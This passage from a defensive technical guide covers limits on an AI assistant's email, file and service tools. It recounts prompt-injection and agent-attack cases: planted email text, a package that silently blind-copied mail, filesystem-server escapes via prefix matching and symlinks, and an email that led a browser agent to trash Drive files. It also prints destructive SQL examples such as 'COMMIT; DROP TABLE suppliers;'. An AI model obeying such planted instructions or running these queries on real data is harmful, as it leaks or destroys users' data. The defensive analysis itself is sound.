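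The list has no scope for drafting alone. An assistant that is only allowed to write drafts still needs a token that permits sending, so the runtime has to block sending. Scopes also cannot distinguish a reply from a forward, restrict messages to particular recipients or domains, or limit the number of messages.

The scopes for reading mail are also coarse. `gmail.metadata` withholds the body but includes the headers, including the subject line, where Nassi and colleagues put their planted text when they attacked through Gmail. `gmail.readonly` covers the whole mailbox, including password-reset links. In Tom's Guide's *3 accounts you should think twice about letting an AI agent access*, Rishi Bhargava, co-founder of the identity company Descope, says those links are why email access is so dangerous. An operator who wants to keep these links from the model has to filter them out of the tool's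 results.

### Matching addresses and limiting volume

Scopes can't specify recipients, so the runtime needs its own list of allowed recipients. A list of domains is short and easy to maintain, and it works well for the company's own domain. Individual addresses are better for people outside the company, because allowing a supplier's domain permits everyone who works there, and allowing `gmail.com` permits almost anyone.

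The runtime has to compare the whole domain. A check that searches for `firm.example` anywhere in the address will accept `firm.example.attacker.test`, and one that tests only the ending will accept `notfirm.example`. The runtime should also ignore the display name, which the sender can set to anything, and reject line breaks, which could let an attacker add another header such as `bcc`.

The runtime should normalize addresses before comparing them, so that `Firm.Example` and `firm.example` match. But it should compare the address it will actually use, without converting lookalike letters. The Cyrillic "а" looks the same as the Latin "a" but belongs to a different address. If the check converted the Cyrillic letter to the Latin one and the mail server then used the original, the message would pass the check and go to the attacker. Converting lookalikes is still useful for raising an alarm.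 If an address isn't on the list but looks like one that is, the runtime should refuse the call without asking a person, who would probably misread the address.

Volume limits reduce the damage when the other rules fail. The operator can cap the number of messages per task and the number of new recipients per day. The mail service's own limits are a poor substitute. Anthropic's *Use Google Workspace connectors*, for example, refers to Google's API quotas, which aren't based on what one employee's task needs. A limit of 20 recipients would slow a spam run or an email worm, but it wouldn't stop a single email containing a stolen document.

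### The email server that copied every message

All of these checks depend on the tool sending what the runtime approved. In September 2025, a widely downloaded package called `postmark-mcp` did not. It let AI assistants send email through Postmark, an email delivery service, but Postmark had no part in it. An outside developer had copied Postmark's official code, which is on GitHub, and published it under the same name on npm, a public library of software packages.

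The package worked properly for 15 versions. Version 1.0.16, released on September 17 according to The Hacker News' *First Malicious MCP Server Found* (2025), added one line of code that blind-copied every email to an address at the developer's domain. The security company Koi noticed the change. The developer deleted the package from npm, but installed copies kept working and copying mail.

Koi counted about 1,500 downloads a week. It guessed that a fifth of them were in active use, which would be about 300 organizations, and that each sent 10 to 50 emails a day. That gives 3,000 to 15,000 stolen emails daily. The total is very uncertain because download counts are a poor measure of how many people use a package.

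In this attack, the model proposed an ordinary email to an ordinary recipient, and the tool added the extra address after any runtime checks had finished. The attacker planted no instructions for the model. An employee who approved the email beforehand would also have seen nothing wrong. A volume limit wouldn't have helped, because each organization was sending its normal amount of mail.

A check placed after the tool would have stopped this. The company can route the tool's outgoing requests through a gateway it controls, which compares the actual recipients with those in the approved call and blocks the message if they differ. A simpler precaution is to fix the tool at a known version and read the changes before each update. Only one line was new, so a reviewer would have had a good chance of spotting it.

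### How current assistants handle sending

By late 2026, the major assistants could all send email, and their makers relied mainly on asking the user first. Claude's Gmail connector gained the ability to send email in August 2026, 9to5Google reported. By default, Claude asks for approval before it sends, replies to or forwards an email. In Auto mode, it can do these things without asking unless an automated check flags the action as risky or the organization requires approval. Anthropic acknowledges that this check can miss risky actions. On Team and Enterprise plans, the organization's owners decide whether members can turn off approval requests. Engadget's *Claude can help manage your email inbox* recommends leaving them on, partly because Claude can make mistakes in an email even when no attacker is involved.

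Before sending an email or scheduling a meeting in Docs, Gmail and Google's other office apps, Gemini shows a preview card that the user can edit, according to Google's *Create content, schedule events, and coordinate tasks across Workspace* (2026). Google's more independent agent, Spark, can run scheduled tasks while the user is away. Google's *Use Gemini Spark to manage your tasks and workflows in Gemini Apps* says Spark is designed to ask before it sends communications, but warns that planted text could make it send a user's emails to an outside service.

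ChatGPT offers more levels. OpenAI's *Managing app permissions in ChatGPT* lists settings that ask about everything, allow reading, allow low-risk actions or allow all actions. Some actions, such as sending an email, may need extra review, and ChatGPT may refuse some requests without offering the user a choice. In TechRadar's *I sent an email without opening Gmail thanks to ChatGPT's new feature*, ChatGPT showed the reporter the email and waited for a click on "Allow". It couldn't attach a file, which was inconvenient but removed one way to leak data.

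These settings apply to kinds of action, such as sending, not to particular recipients. Once a user turns off the approval prompts, emails to a known contact and to a stranger fall under the same permission. An operator who wants to treat them differently has to add recipient rules in the runtime or at the mail server.

### Five proposed sends

Suppose the office assistant's operator adopts these rules. The assistant can send messages to addresses in the company directory without approval, and to listed supplier contacts when it is replying. It needs the employee's approval for any other outside address that she typed herself or that belongs to a thread she asked it to answer. The runtime refuses all other addresses, lookalikes of listed addresses, and any `bcc` she didn't ask for. Files marked "internal" can't be sent outside the company.

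| The employee's request | What the assistant proposes | Rule that applies | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|
| "Send the quarterly report to Alice." | An email to `alice@firm.example` with the report | Alice is in the directory | Allowed |
| "Mail the receipt to my manager." | An email to the manager, with a `bcc` to an address from the invoice | She asked for no `bcc` | Refused |
| "Answer Alice's email." | A reply to `alice@flrm.example`, the reply-to address of the incoming message | The address is a lookalike | Refused |
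| "Tell everyone on the thread that the delivery date works." | A reply to a listed supplier contact and to an unknown address that the supplier copied in | The unknown address belongs to the thread | Employee decides |
| "Forward the contract email to `dana@audit.example`." | A forward with both attachments, the contract and a price list marked "internal" | Internal files can't leave | Refused |

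In the receipt example, it is safer for the runtime to refuse the whole call than to remove the `bcc` and send the rest. The extra address suggests that text in the invoice has influenced the call, and that text may also have changed the body or the attachment. After the refusal, the assistant can propose a new email without the extra address, which the runtime will allow.

The unknown address on the supplier's thread is less suspicious, since people often copy in colleagues. Refusing every such reply would make the assistant tiresome to use, so the employee gets a question that names the new address. In the auditor example, the assistant can try again with the contract alone, but the employee must approve that email because Dana is outside the company.

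### Harmful messages to permitted recipients

Suppose an instruction planted in an invoice leads the assistant to email a colleague in accounting, saying that a supplier has changed banks and giving a new account number. The colleague is in the directory, the email has no attachment, and the assistant sends no other email that hour. Every recipient rule lets the email through, and the colleague has good reason to believe it because it comes from the employee's real account.

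A worm can exploit the same gap. Nassi and colleagues describe, but do not demonstrate, one that would collect contacts from a victim's email and send them the same planted instructions. A list of permitted recipients built from past correspondence would include many of those contacts. An honest mistake can also get through, such as when the assistant includes one supplier's prices in a reply to another. The runtime can search outgoing text for account numbers or confidential markings, but this can't confirm whether the supplier has changed banks.

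## Setting limits on file tools

The main rule for a file tool is usually a list of folders the agent may use. Before the runtime can apply any rule about folders, it has to find out which file the path in a call leads to. Comparing the text of the path with the list isn't enough, because a path can lead to a different place than its text suggests.

### Finding the file a path leads to

Suppose an agent may use only the folder `/work/project`, and it proposes to read `/work/project/../payroll.txt`. The two dots mean "go up one folder", so the path leads to `/work/payroll.txt`, outside the permitted folder. A *symbolic link*, a file that redirects to another location, can also lead outside the folder, but the path doesn't show it. If `/work/project/latest` is a link to `/work/archive`, a request for `/work/project/latest/q3.txt` opens `/work/archive/q3.txt`.

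A correct check has four steps:

1. Make the path absolute, by putting the current folder in front of it if it doesn't start at the top of the disk.
2. Follow the path from left to right, replacing each symbolic link with its target and going up one folder at each `..`.
3. Do the same for the permitted folder, since its own path may contain a link.
4. Split both real locations into components, the names between the slashes, and compare them in order.

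If the permitted folder has the components $f_1, \dots, f_k$ and the file's real location has the components $p_1, \dots, p_n$, the file passes when

$$n \geq k \;\land\; p_i = f_i \text{ for every } i \leq k$$

Some programs shorten step 4 and only test whether the text of the path begins with the text of the permitted folder. This *prefix matching* gives the right answer most of the time:

| Requested path | Real location | Prefix matching | Comparing components |
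|---|---|---|---|
| `/work/project/q3.txt` | `/work/project/q3.txt` | Accepts | Accepts |
| `/work/project/../payroll.txt` | `/work/payroll.txt` | Refuses | Refuses |
| `/work/project/latest/q3.txt` | `/work/archive/q3.txt` | Refuses | Refuses |
| `/work/project-secret/keys.txt` | `/work/project-secret/keys.txt` | Accepts | Refuses |

The last path begins with the string `/work/project`, so prefix matching allows it. Component comparison rejects it because its second component is `project-secret`, not `project`.

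The order of work in step 2 also matters. A program that simplifies the path's text before following links will cancel `latest/..` in `/work/project/latest/../budget.txt` and treat the file as inside the permitted folder. Linux follows the `latest` link to `/work/archive` first, then goes up one level and opens `/work/budget.txt`. Windows resolves such paths differently, according to *Traversal-resistant file APIs* (Neil, 2025), a post on the Go programming language's blog. Windows also reserves some file names, so a program that tries to create a file called `CONOUT$` will print to the screen instead. With so many special cases, operators are better off using a maintained library than writing their own check.

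### The filesystem-server flaws of 2025

Anthropic's reference MCP server for files lets an agent read, write, move and search files inside folders that the user lists. In *EscapeRoute*, a disclosure from the security company Cymulate, Beber describes two ways out of those folders that he found in March 2025. They relied on a prefix-matching flaw and a flaw in how the server handled links.

For the first, Beber configured the server to allow `/private/tmp/allow_dir`. He then asked Claude to list `/private/tmp/allow_dir_sensitive_credentials`, a separate folder beside it. The server checked only whether the requested path started with the allowed path, so it gave access.

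The second flaw was in the error handling. The server resolved symbolic links and raised an error when a link's target was outside the permitted folders. But the code that caught this error was meant for files the agent wants to create, which have no real location to check yet, so it checked the parent folder instead. For a link, it checked the folder containing the link, which passed, and ignored the target. Beber put a link to `/etc/sudoers`, the file that determines who may run commands as administrator, in a folder called `allow_dir_evil`, and the server opened the file.

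He then used a link to write a *launch agent*, a settings file that macOS reads at login to start programs. The Calculator app opened at the next login. An attacker who could write that one file could have run any other program the same way.

An attacker could have exploited the first flaw with planted text alone, because the attack required only a path. The second flaw also required a link, which a person with a low-privilege account on the same computer created by hand in the demonstration. Glama's *Filesystem MCP Server*, a copy of the server's documentation, lists no tool for making links, so an attacker using only an email would have needed an existing link or another tool that could create one, such as a shell.

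Beber reported both flaws on March 30, and Anthropic released the fix, version 2025.7.1, on July 1. OSV's advisories, *GHSA-hc55-p739-j48w* (2025) and *GHSA-q66q-fx2p-7w4m* (2025), give each flaw a severity score of 7.3 out of 10. The US cybersecurity agency CISA had recorded no exploitation of the link flaw as of July 2, according to GCVE's *CVE-2025-53109* (2025).

During the tests, Claude checked the folder it had just opened against its list of allowed folders and said that the access might be a security vulnerability. It was right, but the server had already returned the folder's contents.

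### When the file changes after the check

Even a correct check can fail if the tool opens the file a moment later. Suppose the agent asks to read `/work/project/summary.txt`:

1. The runtime resolves the path, finds an ordinary file in the permitted folder and approves the call.
2. Another program replaces `summary.txt` with a symbolic link to `/work/project-secret/keys.txt`.
3. The tool opens `/work/project/summary.txt`, and the operating system follows the new link to the keys.

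Programmers call this a time-of-check to time-of-use race. Exploiting it requires the ability to change files on the same computer. Neil points out that there are ways to get this access even on a laptop with one user. For example, an unpacking program can extract a symbolic link from an archive and then write the next file through it. An agent with a shell can also start a script that keeps running while the agent makes its next call.

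Making the check part of opening the file closes the gap, which checking twice only shortens. The program keeps the permitted folder open and has the operating system look up every path relative to it, refusing any step that leads outside. Go has offered this through `os.Root` since version 1.24. Linux has a similar option, `RESOLVE_BENEATH`. According to Linux man-pages' *openat2(2)*, if the kernel, the core of the operating system, can't confirm that a `..` stayed inside the folder, it returns an error and the program may try again.

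Both methods have limits. `RESOLVE_BENEATH` rejects every link that gives an absolute path, even one that leads back into the permitted folder, so some legitimate files won't open. Neither method alone blocks access through a *bind mount*, which makes one folder appear inside another. Creating a bind mount normally takes administrator rights, so this matters mostly to operators who set one up and forget about it. Linux has a separate option that blocks access through bind mounts.

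### Sandboxes enforced by the operating system

A path check in a file tool covers only the calls that go through that tool. If the agent can also run shell commands or scripts, those can open files directly and bypass the check. A *sandbox* closes this gap by having the operating system restrict the whole process. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) describes a sandbox for Claude Code that lets the agent read and write in the current working folder and blocks changes to files anywhere else. Anthropic notes that the restrictions also cover any scripts and programs that a command starts.

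A sandbox also makes the agent less tiresome to use, because routine work inside the folder no longer needs permission. Anthropic reported 84 percent fewer permission prompts, according to InfoQ (2026). When code runs in the claude.ai chat app, Anthropic uses a temporary container on its own servers that has no access to the user's disk.

Operators need to check that the sandbox is running. If a required package is missing or the platform is unsupported, Claude Code by default shows a warning and runs commands without the sandbox. The `sandbox.failIfUnavailable` setting makes it stop instead. An organization that relies on the sandbox should turn this setting on, since developers may not read the warning. OpenAI similarly restricts its own staff to the two sandboxed modes of its coding agent, Codex.

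An agent that can't write outside a folder may still be able to read files outside it, and the permitted folder may contain secrets. Software projects often keep passwords in a file called `.env`. The reference MCP server doesn't block such files inside allowed folders, according to a comparison published on Glama in November 2026 by a rival server's developer. A list of allowed folders therefore needs exceptions. An example in OpenAI's *Permissions* makes the project folder writable, the `.devcontainer` settings folder read-only and every `.env` file unreadable.

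One fixed sandbox can also be too coarse. Adam, Lu and colleagues (2026) point out in *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* that the right limits change from task to task, and that users soon switch off a sandbox that gets in their way. They propose a small sandbox around each operation in a tool's code that reads, writes or sends something. The runtime would send a policy with each call, such as "write only to the workspace", and an automatic analysis of the code would check that the developer hadn't left any operation unprotected. In an early test on one real MCP server, their prototype found unprotected operations. Because the evidence is still limited and the approach depends on thousands of tool developers adding the sandboxes, most operators will for now have to combine a fixed sandbox with path rules in the runtime.

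### Files on a cloud drive

An operating-system sandbox is little help with a cloud drive, because reading, deleting and sharing are all requests to the same outside service. If the sandbox lets the agent reach Google Drive, it usually can't tell these requests apart.

Path rules don't carry over well to Google Drive either. Google's *Files and folders overview* explains that Drive identifies each file by an ID that stays the same when somebody renames the file. One file can be in several folders, and a shortcut can point to a file somewhere else. The runtime should therefore look up the file's ID once, follow any shortcut to its target, and then check that file's folders, owner and readers. It should pass the tool the ID rather than the name, because a supplier who can upload to a folder can give a file the same name as the quarterly report.

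The access token gives the operator a second way to limit the agent. Drive scopes differ in how many files they cover:

| Scope | Files it covers | What the holder may do |
|---|---|---|
| `drive` | The whole drive | Nearly everything the user can do, including deleting and sharing |
| `drive.readonly` | The whole drive | See and download files, and see whom the user shares them with |
| `drive.metadata.readonly` | The whole drive | See titles, descriptions, folders and the people with access |
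| `drive.file` | Files the user opens or creates with the app | View and manage those files |

Google's *Requesting Minimum Scopes* recommends `drive.file` for most apps. The user chooses a file in a selection window, and the app gets access to only that file. This resembles Hardy's capability, since choosing the file also gives the app the right to use it. A planted instruction can't make the app access the rest of the drive because the app's token doesn't cover it.

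`drive.file` limits which files the agent can use but not what it does with them. According to Google, it still lets the agent permanently delete a file the user has chosen. It also doesn't suit jobs like finding a report among thousands of files, where the assistant can't ask the user to choose the file first. The operator can instead give the search tool a `drive.readonly` token and give the tools that change files a separate `drive.file` token. The agent could then read files the user hadn't selected, but not change them.

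Sharing is the other big difference from a local disk. A Drive permission can give access to one person, a group, everyone at a company or anyone at all, and it can cover a single file or a folder and everything in it. Each new reader receives data as an email recipient does, so the recipient rules for messages apply here too. Unlike an email recipient, though, a person with access to a shared file also sees later changes to it. Moving a file into a shared folder can also give it new readers, without any call to a sharing tool. The runtime should check who can read the destination folder and treat the move as sharing if the file would gain readers.

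### Sorting writes by consequence

A permitted folder determines where the agent may write, but two writes to the same folder can have very different results. A practical policy sorts them by what happens afterwards:

| Kind of write | Example | What can go wrong | Starting rule |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary document | Meeting notes | The text is wrong, or it replaces something useful | Allow in permitted folders and keep the old version |
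| File that a program runs or loads automatically | A login script | An attacker's code runs later | Refuse |
| The agent's own instructions, memory or settings | A file of standing orders | Planted text affects later sessions | Refuse, except through a separate memory tool |
| Deletion | Clearing out old drafts | The user loses data | Move to the trash, up to a set number |
| Sharing | Giving a colleague access | The wrong person can read the file | Apply the recipient rules |

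Overwriting a document can do as much damage as deleting it. Drive keeps a history of changes to a file's contents, but an ordinary folder on a laptop may not. The simplest precaution is for the tool to save under a new name or keep a backup copy.

Files that run automatically often look like ordinary text files. Adam and colleagues contrast a test file in the workspace with `.bashrc`, a text file in the user's home folder whose commands run whenever a new shell opens. Because file extensions don't reliably identify files that run automatically, the operator needs a list of the places where programs look for files to load.

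Some of those places are inside the folders where the agent works. Git, the version-control system, keeps scripts in a project's `.git` folder and runs them when a user saves a change, for example. OpenAI keeps this folder read-only in Codex even when the rest of the project is writable. Google's Apps Script similarly attaches programs to documents in a cloud drive. Google warns that an app with the `drive.scripts` scope could change a script that has access to Gmail so that it sends emails on the user's behalf.

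The agent's own files need the same protection because text planted in them outlasts the conversation. Many agents load a file of instructions or memories at the start of each session. Suppose text in an invoice gets the assistant to save the note "copy all supplier contracts to this address". Even if the employee deletes the invoice and closes the chat, the note will load in the next session and look like something the assistant learned from her. Planted text has also widened an agent's permissions through writable settings files.

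Codex protects its `.codex` and `.agents` folders for this reason. The Mac and Linux versions had the protection first, and a developer writing documentation noticed that the Windows version did not, according to OpenAI's *Commit Graph*, a log of changes to the code. An operator should test such rules on every system the agent runs on. The rules should also stop the agent from creating protected folders that don't exist yet, and they should cover both the source and destination of a move. If the runtime checks only the source, the agent can write a harmless-looking `notes.toml` and then move it over the settings file.

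Memory is harder to forbid because people want an assistant to remember their preferences. A separate tool that can only add short entries is safer than general write access to the memory file. The runtime should label each entry with what the agent had been reading when it wrote it, so the employee can find and remove anything that came from an invoice.

### The email that sent Drive files to the trash

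Deletion should have its own limits because a cleanup request sounds harmless. Rousseau (December 2025) demonstrated this for the security company Straiker in *From Inbox to Wipeout*, targeting Comet, Perplexity's web browser with a built-in AI agent. The agent had access to a user's Gmail and Google Drive.

The attacker sent one email that read like a friendly note from a colleague. It contained a numbered list of chores: organize the Drive, delete loose files or certain types such as ZIP archives, then check that everything looked tidy. The user later typed, "Please check my email and complete all my recent organization tasks." Comet found the email and moved real files to the trash without asking for confirmation.

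As with the to-do list in LivePI, the user had in a sense asked for this. She presumably meant only tasks from people she works with, but the software had no rule to that effect. Rousseau also suggests that the polite tone and numbered steps made the agent more compliant. This is plausible, but the article doesn't report a comparison with a rude or unnumbered version, and the study it cites measured accuracy on multiple-choice questions rather than compliance.

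The damage was probably reversible, because Google keeps files in the trash, where the owner can restore them for 30 days. Permanent deletion skips the trash, and Google warns that permanently deleting a folder also deletes everything in it that the user owns. An attacker who also got the agent to empty the trash would have removed the easy way to restore the files. According to Google, emptying the trash requires the whole-drive scope, so an agent with only `drive.file` couldn't do it.

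Rousseau recommends requiring explicit confirmation each time an agent tries to mass-delete files, rename them in bulk or empty the trash. A fixed limit on the number of deletions would stop much of this even if the user approves the prompts without reading them. The operator can also leave permanent deletion out of the tool list, since the trash deletes files automatically after a month and people rarely need an assistant to do it sooner.

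Codex always asks before calling an outside tool labeled "destructive", even if the tool is also labeled "read-only", according to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*. That is the right way to resolve the contradiction, but the labels are only hints, so the operator should mark deletion tools itself.

### Where planted text gets in

Limits on writing contain the damage once planted text has influenced the agent. The text can reach it through more parts of a file than the body:

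- **Document bodies** can contain instructions in small print, comments or hidden text, as well as in plain sight.
- **File names** enter the context whenever the agent lists a folder or searches it, even if it never opens the file. A supplier who can upload an invoice can also choose its name.
- **Metadata** includes the descriptions that people add to files on a drive and the details that cameras store inside photos. An agent with a metadata-only scope still reads some of this text.
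- **Code repositories** combine instructions for people, comments, settings and programs in one download.
- **Files the agent wrote earlier** may repeat text from any of these sources.

Like the malicious package in LivePI, code in a repository can do harm before the model reads anything. A post on DEV Community, a site for programmers, describes three vulnerability reports about Claude Code in which code in a project folder ran before the user clicked to trust the folder. It is safer to open an unfamiliar folder read-only and load nothing from it until the user has decided whether to trust it. Codex may start this way, depending on its setup.

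The agent's own files are the easiest source of outside text to overlook. If the agent summarizes a supplier's contract and saves the summary, it becomes the file's author, so a rule based on authorship would mark the supplier's words as trusted. The runtime should record the original source on the new file. If the source of a file's text is unknown, the runtime should treat the file as outside text.

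Planted text can also reach the agent from outside the file tool and direct it to fetch a file. CrowdStrike's *How Agentic Tool Chain Attacks Threaten AI Agent Security* (2026) gives the example of a tool for adding numbers whose description includes an instruction to read the user's private login key and pass it along as a "sidenote". A correct path check would refuse this read, because the key isn't in a permitted folder. The check has to cover every tool that can open a file, which may include the browser. In March 2026, Zenity Labs showed that malicious calendar invitations could make the Comet browser leak files from the user's disk, according to OECD's *Zero-Click Prompt Injection in Perplexity's Comet AI Browser Enables Credential Theft* (2026).

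### The office assistant's file rules

The office assistant works on the company drive, so its operator bases the rules on file IDs. When the employee names a folder, the runtime looks up the folder's ID and allows `read_file` to list and open what is inside. The assistant can also read the shared reports folder at any time. It needs a new request from the employee to read anywhere else, and files that hold passwords are off-limits in every folder.

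If a user asks the assistant to "pay the invoice in my contracts folder and mail the receipt to my manager," these rules let it open the invoice. The receipt is in another folder, but `send_payment` created it during this task and returned its location, so the runtime permits that one file. If the invoice contains an instruction to "verify the amount against the salary file," the assistant may propose to open that file, but the runtime will refuse.

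The invoice might instead lead the assistant to call `share_file` on the whole contracts folder, with the supplier's address as the recipient. The recipient rules already stop this, because the employee never asked to give the supplier access. The operator also forbids sharing any folder, even with colleagues, because someone may later add documents that weren't meant to be shared. When the employee asks the assistant to share the quarterly report with Alice, the runtime allows the call and sets `permission` to "reader". Alice gets editing rights only if the employee asks for them.

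The inventory has no tool for saving or deleting files, and the operator should add one only when the employee needs it. If she wants help clearing out old drafts, the operator could add `trash_file(file_id)`, which would move up to ten files per task from a folder she names to the trash. An email like the one in Rousseau's demonstration could then cause the agent to trash at most ten files from that folder, and she would have a month to restore them.

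A tool for saving notes would need its own folder that other employees can't read and that no program loads anything from. The assistant's instructions and settings would stay on a server that its file tools can't reach. The assistant could write anything in the notes folder, including false information. If a forged invoice gives a new account number and the assistant saves it under the supplier's name, every path rule will allow the write, and next month's payment may use that number.

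## Setting limits on service tools

When a tool call reaches an outside service, such as the company's accounting system, the service runs its own authorization check. The service doesn't have the conversation, so the check is based on the request and the service's stored data about accounts and records. The runtime's rules have to cover what that check leaves out.

### How a service decides

Many services use OAuth, a standard that lets a user give a program limited access without handing over her password. She logs in at an *authorization server* and approves the access that the program asks for. The authorization server then issues an *access token*, a string that the program attaches to each request. When the office assistant asks to change a supplier's phone number, the accounting system goes through four steps:

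1. It checks that the token is genuine, hasn't expired and is meant for this service.
2. It checks that the token's scopes cover the operation, here editing supplier records.
3. It looks up the account that the token stands for.
4. It checks that this account may edit this particular record.

A scope doesn't normally add to what the account can do. If an employee can't open the payroll records, an assistant acting in her name can't either, however broad its scopes are.

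This protection disappears if the agent uses one shared account for everybody. An intern could then ask the assistant for records that only the accountants should see, and step 4 would pass because the shared account can open them. AWS lists this as a common mistake because every call then runs with the agent's permissions instead of the user's. Passing on the employee's identity is better, but it gives the agent access to everything the employee can open, even though most tasks need only a few records.

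None of the four steps takes the task into account. If an employee who is allowed to edit supplier records asks the assistant only to check an invoice, and text in the invoice leads the assistant to change the supplier's bank details, the service will accept the change just as it would if she had asked for it.

### Rules for each operation

The operator can narrow this down by giving each kind of operation its own rule in the runtime:

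| Operation | Example | Starting rule |
|---|---|---|
| Read | Look up a supplier | Allow, but return only the fields the task needs |
| Create | Open a support ticket | Allow up to a set number per task |
| Update | Correct a phone number | Allow for listed fields and ask about the rest |
| Delete | Remove a duplicate supplier | Refuse, or mark the record as inactive instead |
| Pay | Pay an invoice | Limit the account and the amount |

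Updates need rules for individual fields because one scope usually covers the whole record. The operator should treat changes to a supplier's bank details as strictly as payments, because a wrong account diverts every later payment to that supplier, while a wrong phone number is only a nuisance. Creating a user account or API key can also be serious, because it may give an attacker access long after the task is over.

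Some service tools take the service's address as an argument, as in `http_request(url, method, body)`. An attacker who controls `url` can have the data sent to their own server, along with the access token if the runtime attaches it automatically. The runtime should fix each tool's address so the model can't change it, and refuse redirects to other addresses.

### Writing limits in a policy language

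An operator can write these rules in ordinary code, but a policy language keeps them in one place where an auditor can read them. Amazon's AgentCore Policy uses a language called Cedar. Tool calls pass through a *gateway*, a program that applies the rules to each call before forwarding it to the service.

The rule below adapts a refund example from AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies* to the assistant's payment tool. Amounts are in cents, and `company-gateway` stands in for the gateway's full identifier.

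```
permit (
  principal is AgentCore::OAuthUser,
  action == AgentCore::Action::"Accounting___send_payment",
  resource == AgentCore::Gateway::"company-gateway"
)
when {
  principal.hasTag("username") &&
  principal.getTag("username") == "employee-17" &&
  context.input.amount <= 50000
};
```

The lines under `permit` limit the rule to logged-in users who call `send_payment` through this gateway. The `when` part also requires that the user be employee 17 and that the amount be no more than 500. The username comes from the user's access token, so nothing in an invoice can change it. The amount comes from the arguments the model wrote.

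Cedar refuses any call that no rule permits. If a `forbid` rule matches, the gateway refuses the call even if `permit` rules also match. The operator can therefore ban payments to a suspicious account by adding one rule, without first finding every rule that might allow them.

It is easy to make small mistakes in these rules. AWS describes its example as limiting refunds to $500 or less, but the rule tests for `amount < 500`, which blocks a refund of exactly $500. Another AWS sample, generated from a sentence in plain English, checks for the scope `payment:process` with wildcards on both sides, so a token with only a narrower scope called `payment:process_draft` would also pass. Operators should test values at the edge of each limit. AWS suggests first running new rules in a log-only mode, in which the gateway records its decisions without enforcing them.

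According to AWS, a plain AgentCore rule can use only the tool's arguments as context, so it can stop one payment of 5,000 but not ten payments of 490. AWS's *Authoring temporal policies* describes a newer type of rule that also uses earlier calls in the same session. One example allows a transfer only to an account that an earlier lookup returned. Another refuses any transfer that would bring the total to 3,000 or more, so it allows two transfers of 1,000 but not a third.

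These totals reset with each new session, and the caller chooses the session ID. AWS warns that its similar limit on the number of calls is not a security control against a determined caller. A spending limit that must hold should be enforced in the accounting system or at the bank.

### Parsing a database query

Limits on arguments don't work well for a database tool that accepts any query, because the whole operation is inside one string. Suppose the operator wants the agent to read the database but not change it. Searching the query for words like "delete" would block a harmless search for support tickets with that word in the title. Checking how the query begins is no better, as this example for the PostgreSQL database shows:

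```sql
WITH gone AS (DELETE FROM suppliers RETURNING *)
SELECT * FROM gone;
```

The main statement is a `SELECT`, which normally only reads, but the query deletes every supplier and then lists them. A reliable check has to work out the structure of the query:

1. Parse the query with a parser made for that database, and refuse it if parsing fails.
2. Refuse it if it contains more than one statement.
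3. Go through every part, including queries nested inside others, and refuse anything that isn't a read.
4. Compare the tables, columns and functions with a list of permitted ones.

Step 2 matters even if the runtime opens a read-only transaction, in which the database rejects changes, because the query `COMMIT; DROP TABLE suppliers;` ends that transaction and then deletes the table. Functions belong on the list in step 4 because a `SELECT` can call one that changes data.

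The parser may still interpret an unusual query differently from the database, so the tool should log in with a database account that has permission only to read the tables the tool needs. A `DELETE` that gets past the parser will then fail. Even so, a permitted read can return far more data than the task requires.

For most office work, avoiding free-form queries is simpler. A tool like `get_supplier(name)` can run a fixed, parameterized query, so the model only fills in the name. Free-form queries make sense for an analyst whose questions nobody can predict.

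### MCP authorization since July 2026

An agent often reaches a service through an MCP server instead of calling it directly, which adds another place to check tokens. MCP had no authorization framework when it launched in 2024. It gained one based on OAuth in March 2025, as Dhamsania (2026), in *MCP has tightened its authentication rules four times*, recounts. The current rules, in Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026), date from July 28, 2026. They work like this for a server on the web:

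1. The runtime sends a request without a token. The server refuses it and tells the runtime how to find the authorization server. It should also list the scopes that the request needs.
2. The runtime opens a browser window, where the user logs in and approves the access. The runtime's request names the MCP server that the token is for.
3. The authorization server sends back a one-time code. If the response names its issuer, the runtime compares the name with the one it expected, so that it doesn't hand the code to the wrong party.
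4. The runtime exchanges the code for a token and attaches the token to every request.
5. The MCP server accepts the token only if the authorization server issued it for that MCP server.

Binding the token to one server protects the user from the other servers she has connected. Otherwise a malicious calendar server could use the token it received to access the accounting server. An MCP server also may not pass the token it receives on to another service, and must get a separate token if it needs data from that service.

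An agent's permissions tend to grow as it works. When a token lacks a scope that a call needs, the server refuses the call and lists the missing scopes, and the runtime then requests a new token with the old scopes plus the new ones. If text planted in an invoice leads the model to attempt a payment with a read-only token, the employee may see a login page requesting permission to make payments. The runtime should apply its own rules to the call before it requests more scopes.

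Authorization is optional in MCP, and a server on the user's own computer normally takes its credentials from the local environment instead. The July changes apply established OAuth practice to agents and, as the Agentic AI Foundation's *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28* notes, introduce no new kind of authorization. A token still shows only who may use the server and with which scopes.

### Headers that let a gateway decide per tool

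The July revision also makes it easier for a gateway to apply a rule to a single tool. Clients on the web must now copy the type of request and the tool's name into two headers, `Mcp-Method` and `Mcp-Name`, and a server can mark certain arguments for copying too. Körbächer (2026), in *A platform team's guide to MCP 7-28*, gives the example of a rule that allows each customer ten `execute_sql` calls a minute and bans the tool in one region for test machines. Previously a gateway had to parse the body of every request to enforce such a rule, and in most cases he had seen, nobody wrote one.

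The client writes both the headers and the body, and they can differ. *MCP goes stateless with headers. Do you need an MCP-native data plane?* (Posta, 2026) demonstrates this with a gateway that should allow only a harmless tool called `echo`. Posta's request has `echo` in the header but `printEnv` in the body, a tool that prints the server's environment variables, which often include passwords. A gateway that reads only headers would let the request through. Posta writes for a project that makes a body-reading gateway, so he has an interest in the conclusion, but anyone can reproduce the test from his instructions.

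MCP requires servers to reject a request whose headers and body don't match. Older versions of the protocol don't, so Körbächer advises gateways to refuse requests that don't declare the July version. MCP also forbids treating header values as trusted input for security decisions, because a model or a malicious client may have influenced them. Headers are good enough for routing requests and counting calls, but a rule about money should use the amount in the body.

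A gateway that processes request and response bodies can also shorten the list of tools. If a user may use only 2 of a server's 100 tools, the gateway can remove the other 98 before the model receives the list. The model then doesn't waste calls on them, and an attacker who plants instructions in text the model reads has fewer tools to exploit.

### Access managed by the company or by Google

In a large company, approving each MCP server separately is tedious for employees and hard for the security team to supervise. A standard extension that became stable in June 2026 moves the decision to the company's identity provider, the system that employees log in to. *Enterprise-Managed Authorization* (Carleton, 2026) describes how administrators enable a server once and employees get access according to their groups and roles, without seeing a consent page for each server. Okta was the first identity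 provider to support the extension. Anthropic added it to Claude, and the first servers included Asana, Atlassian, Figma and Linear.

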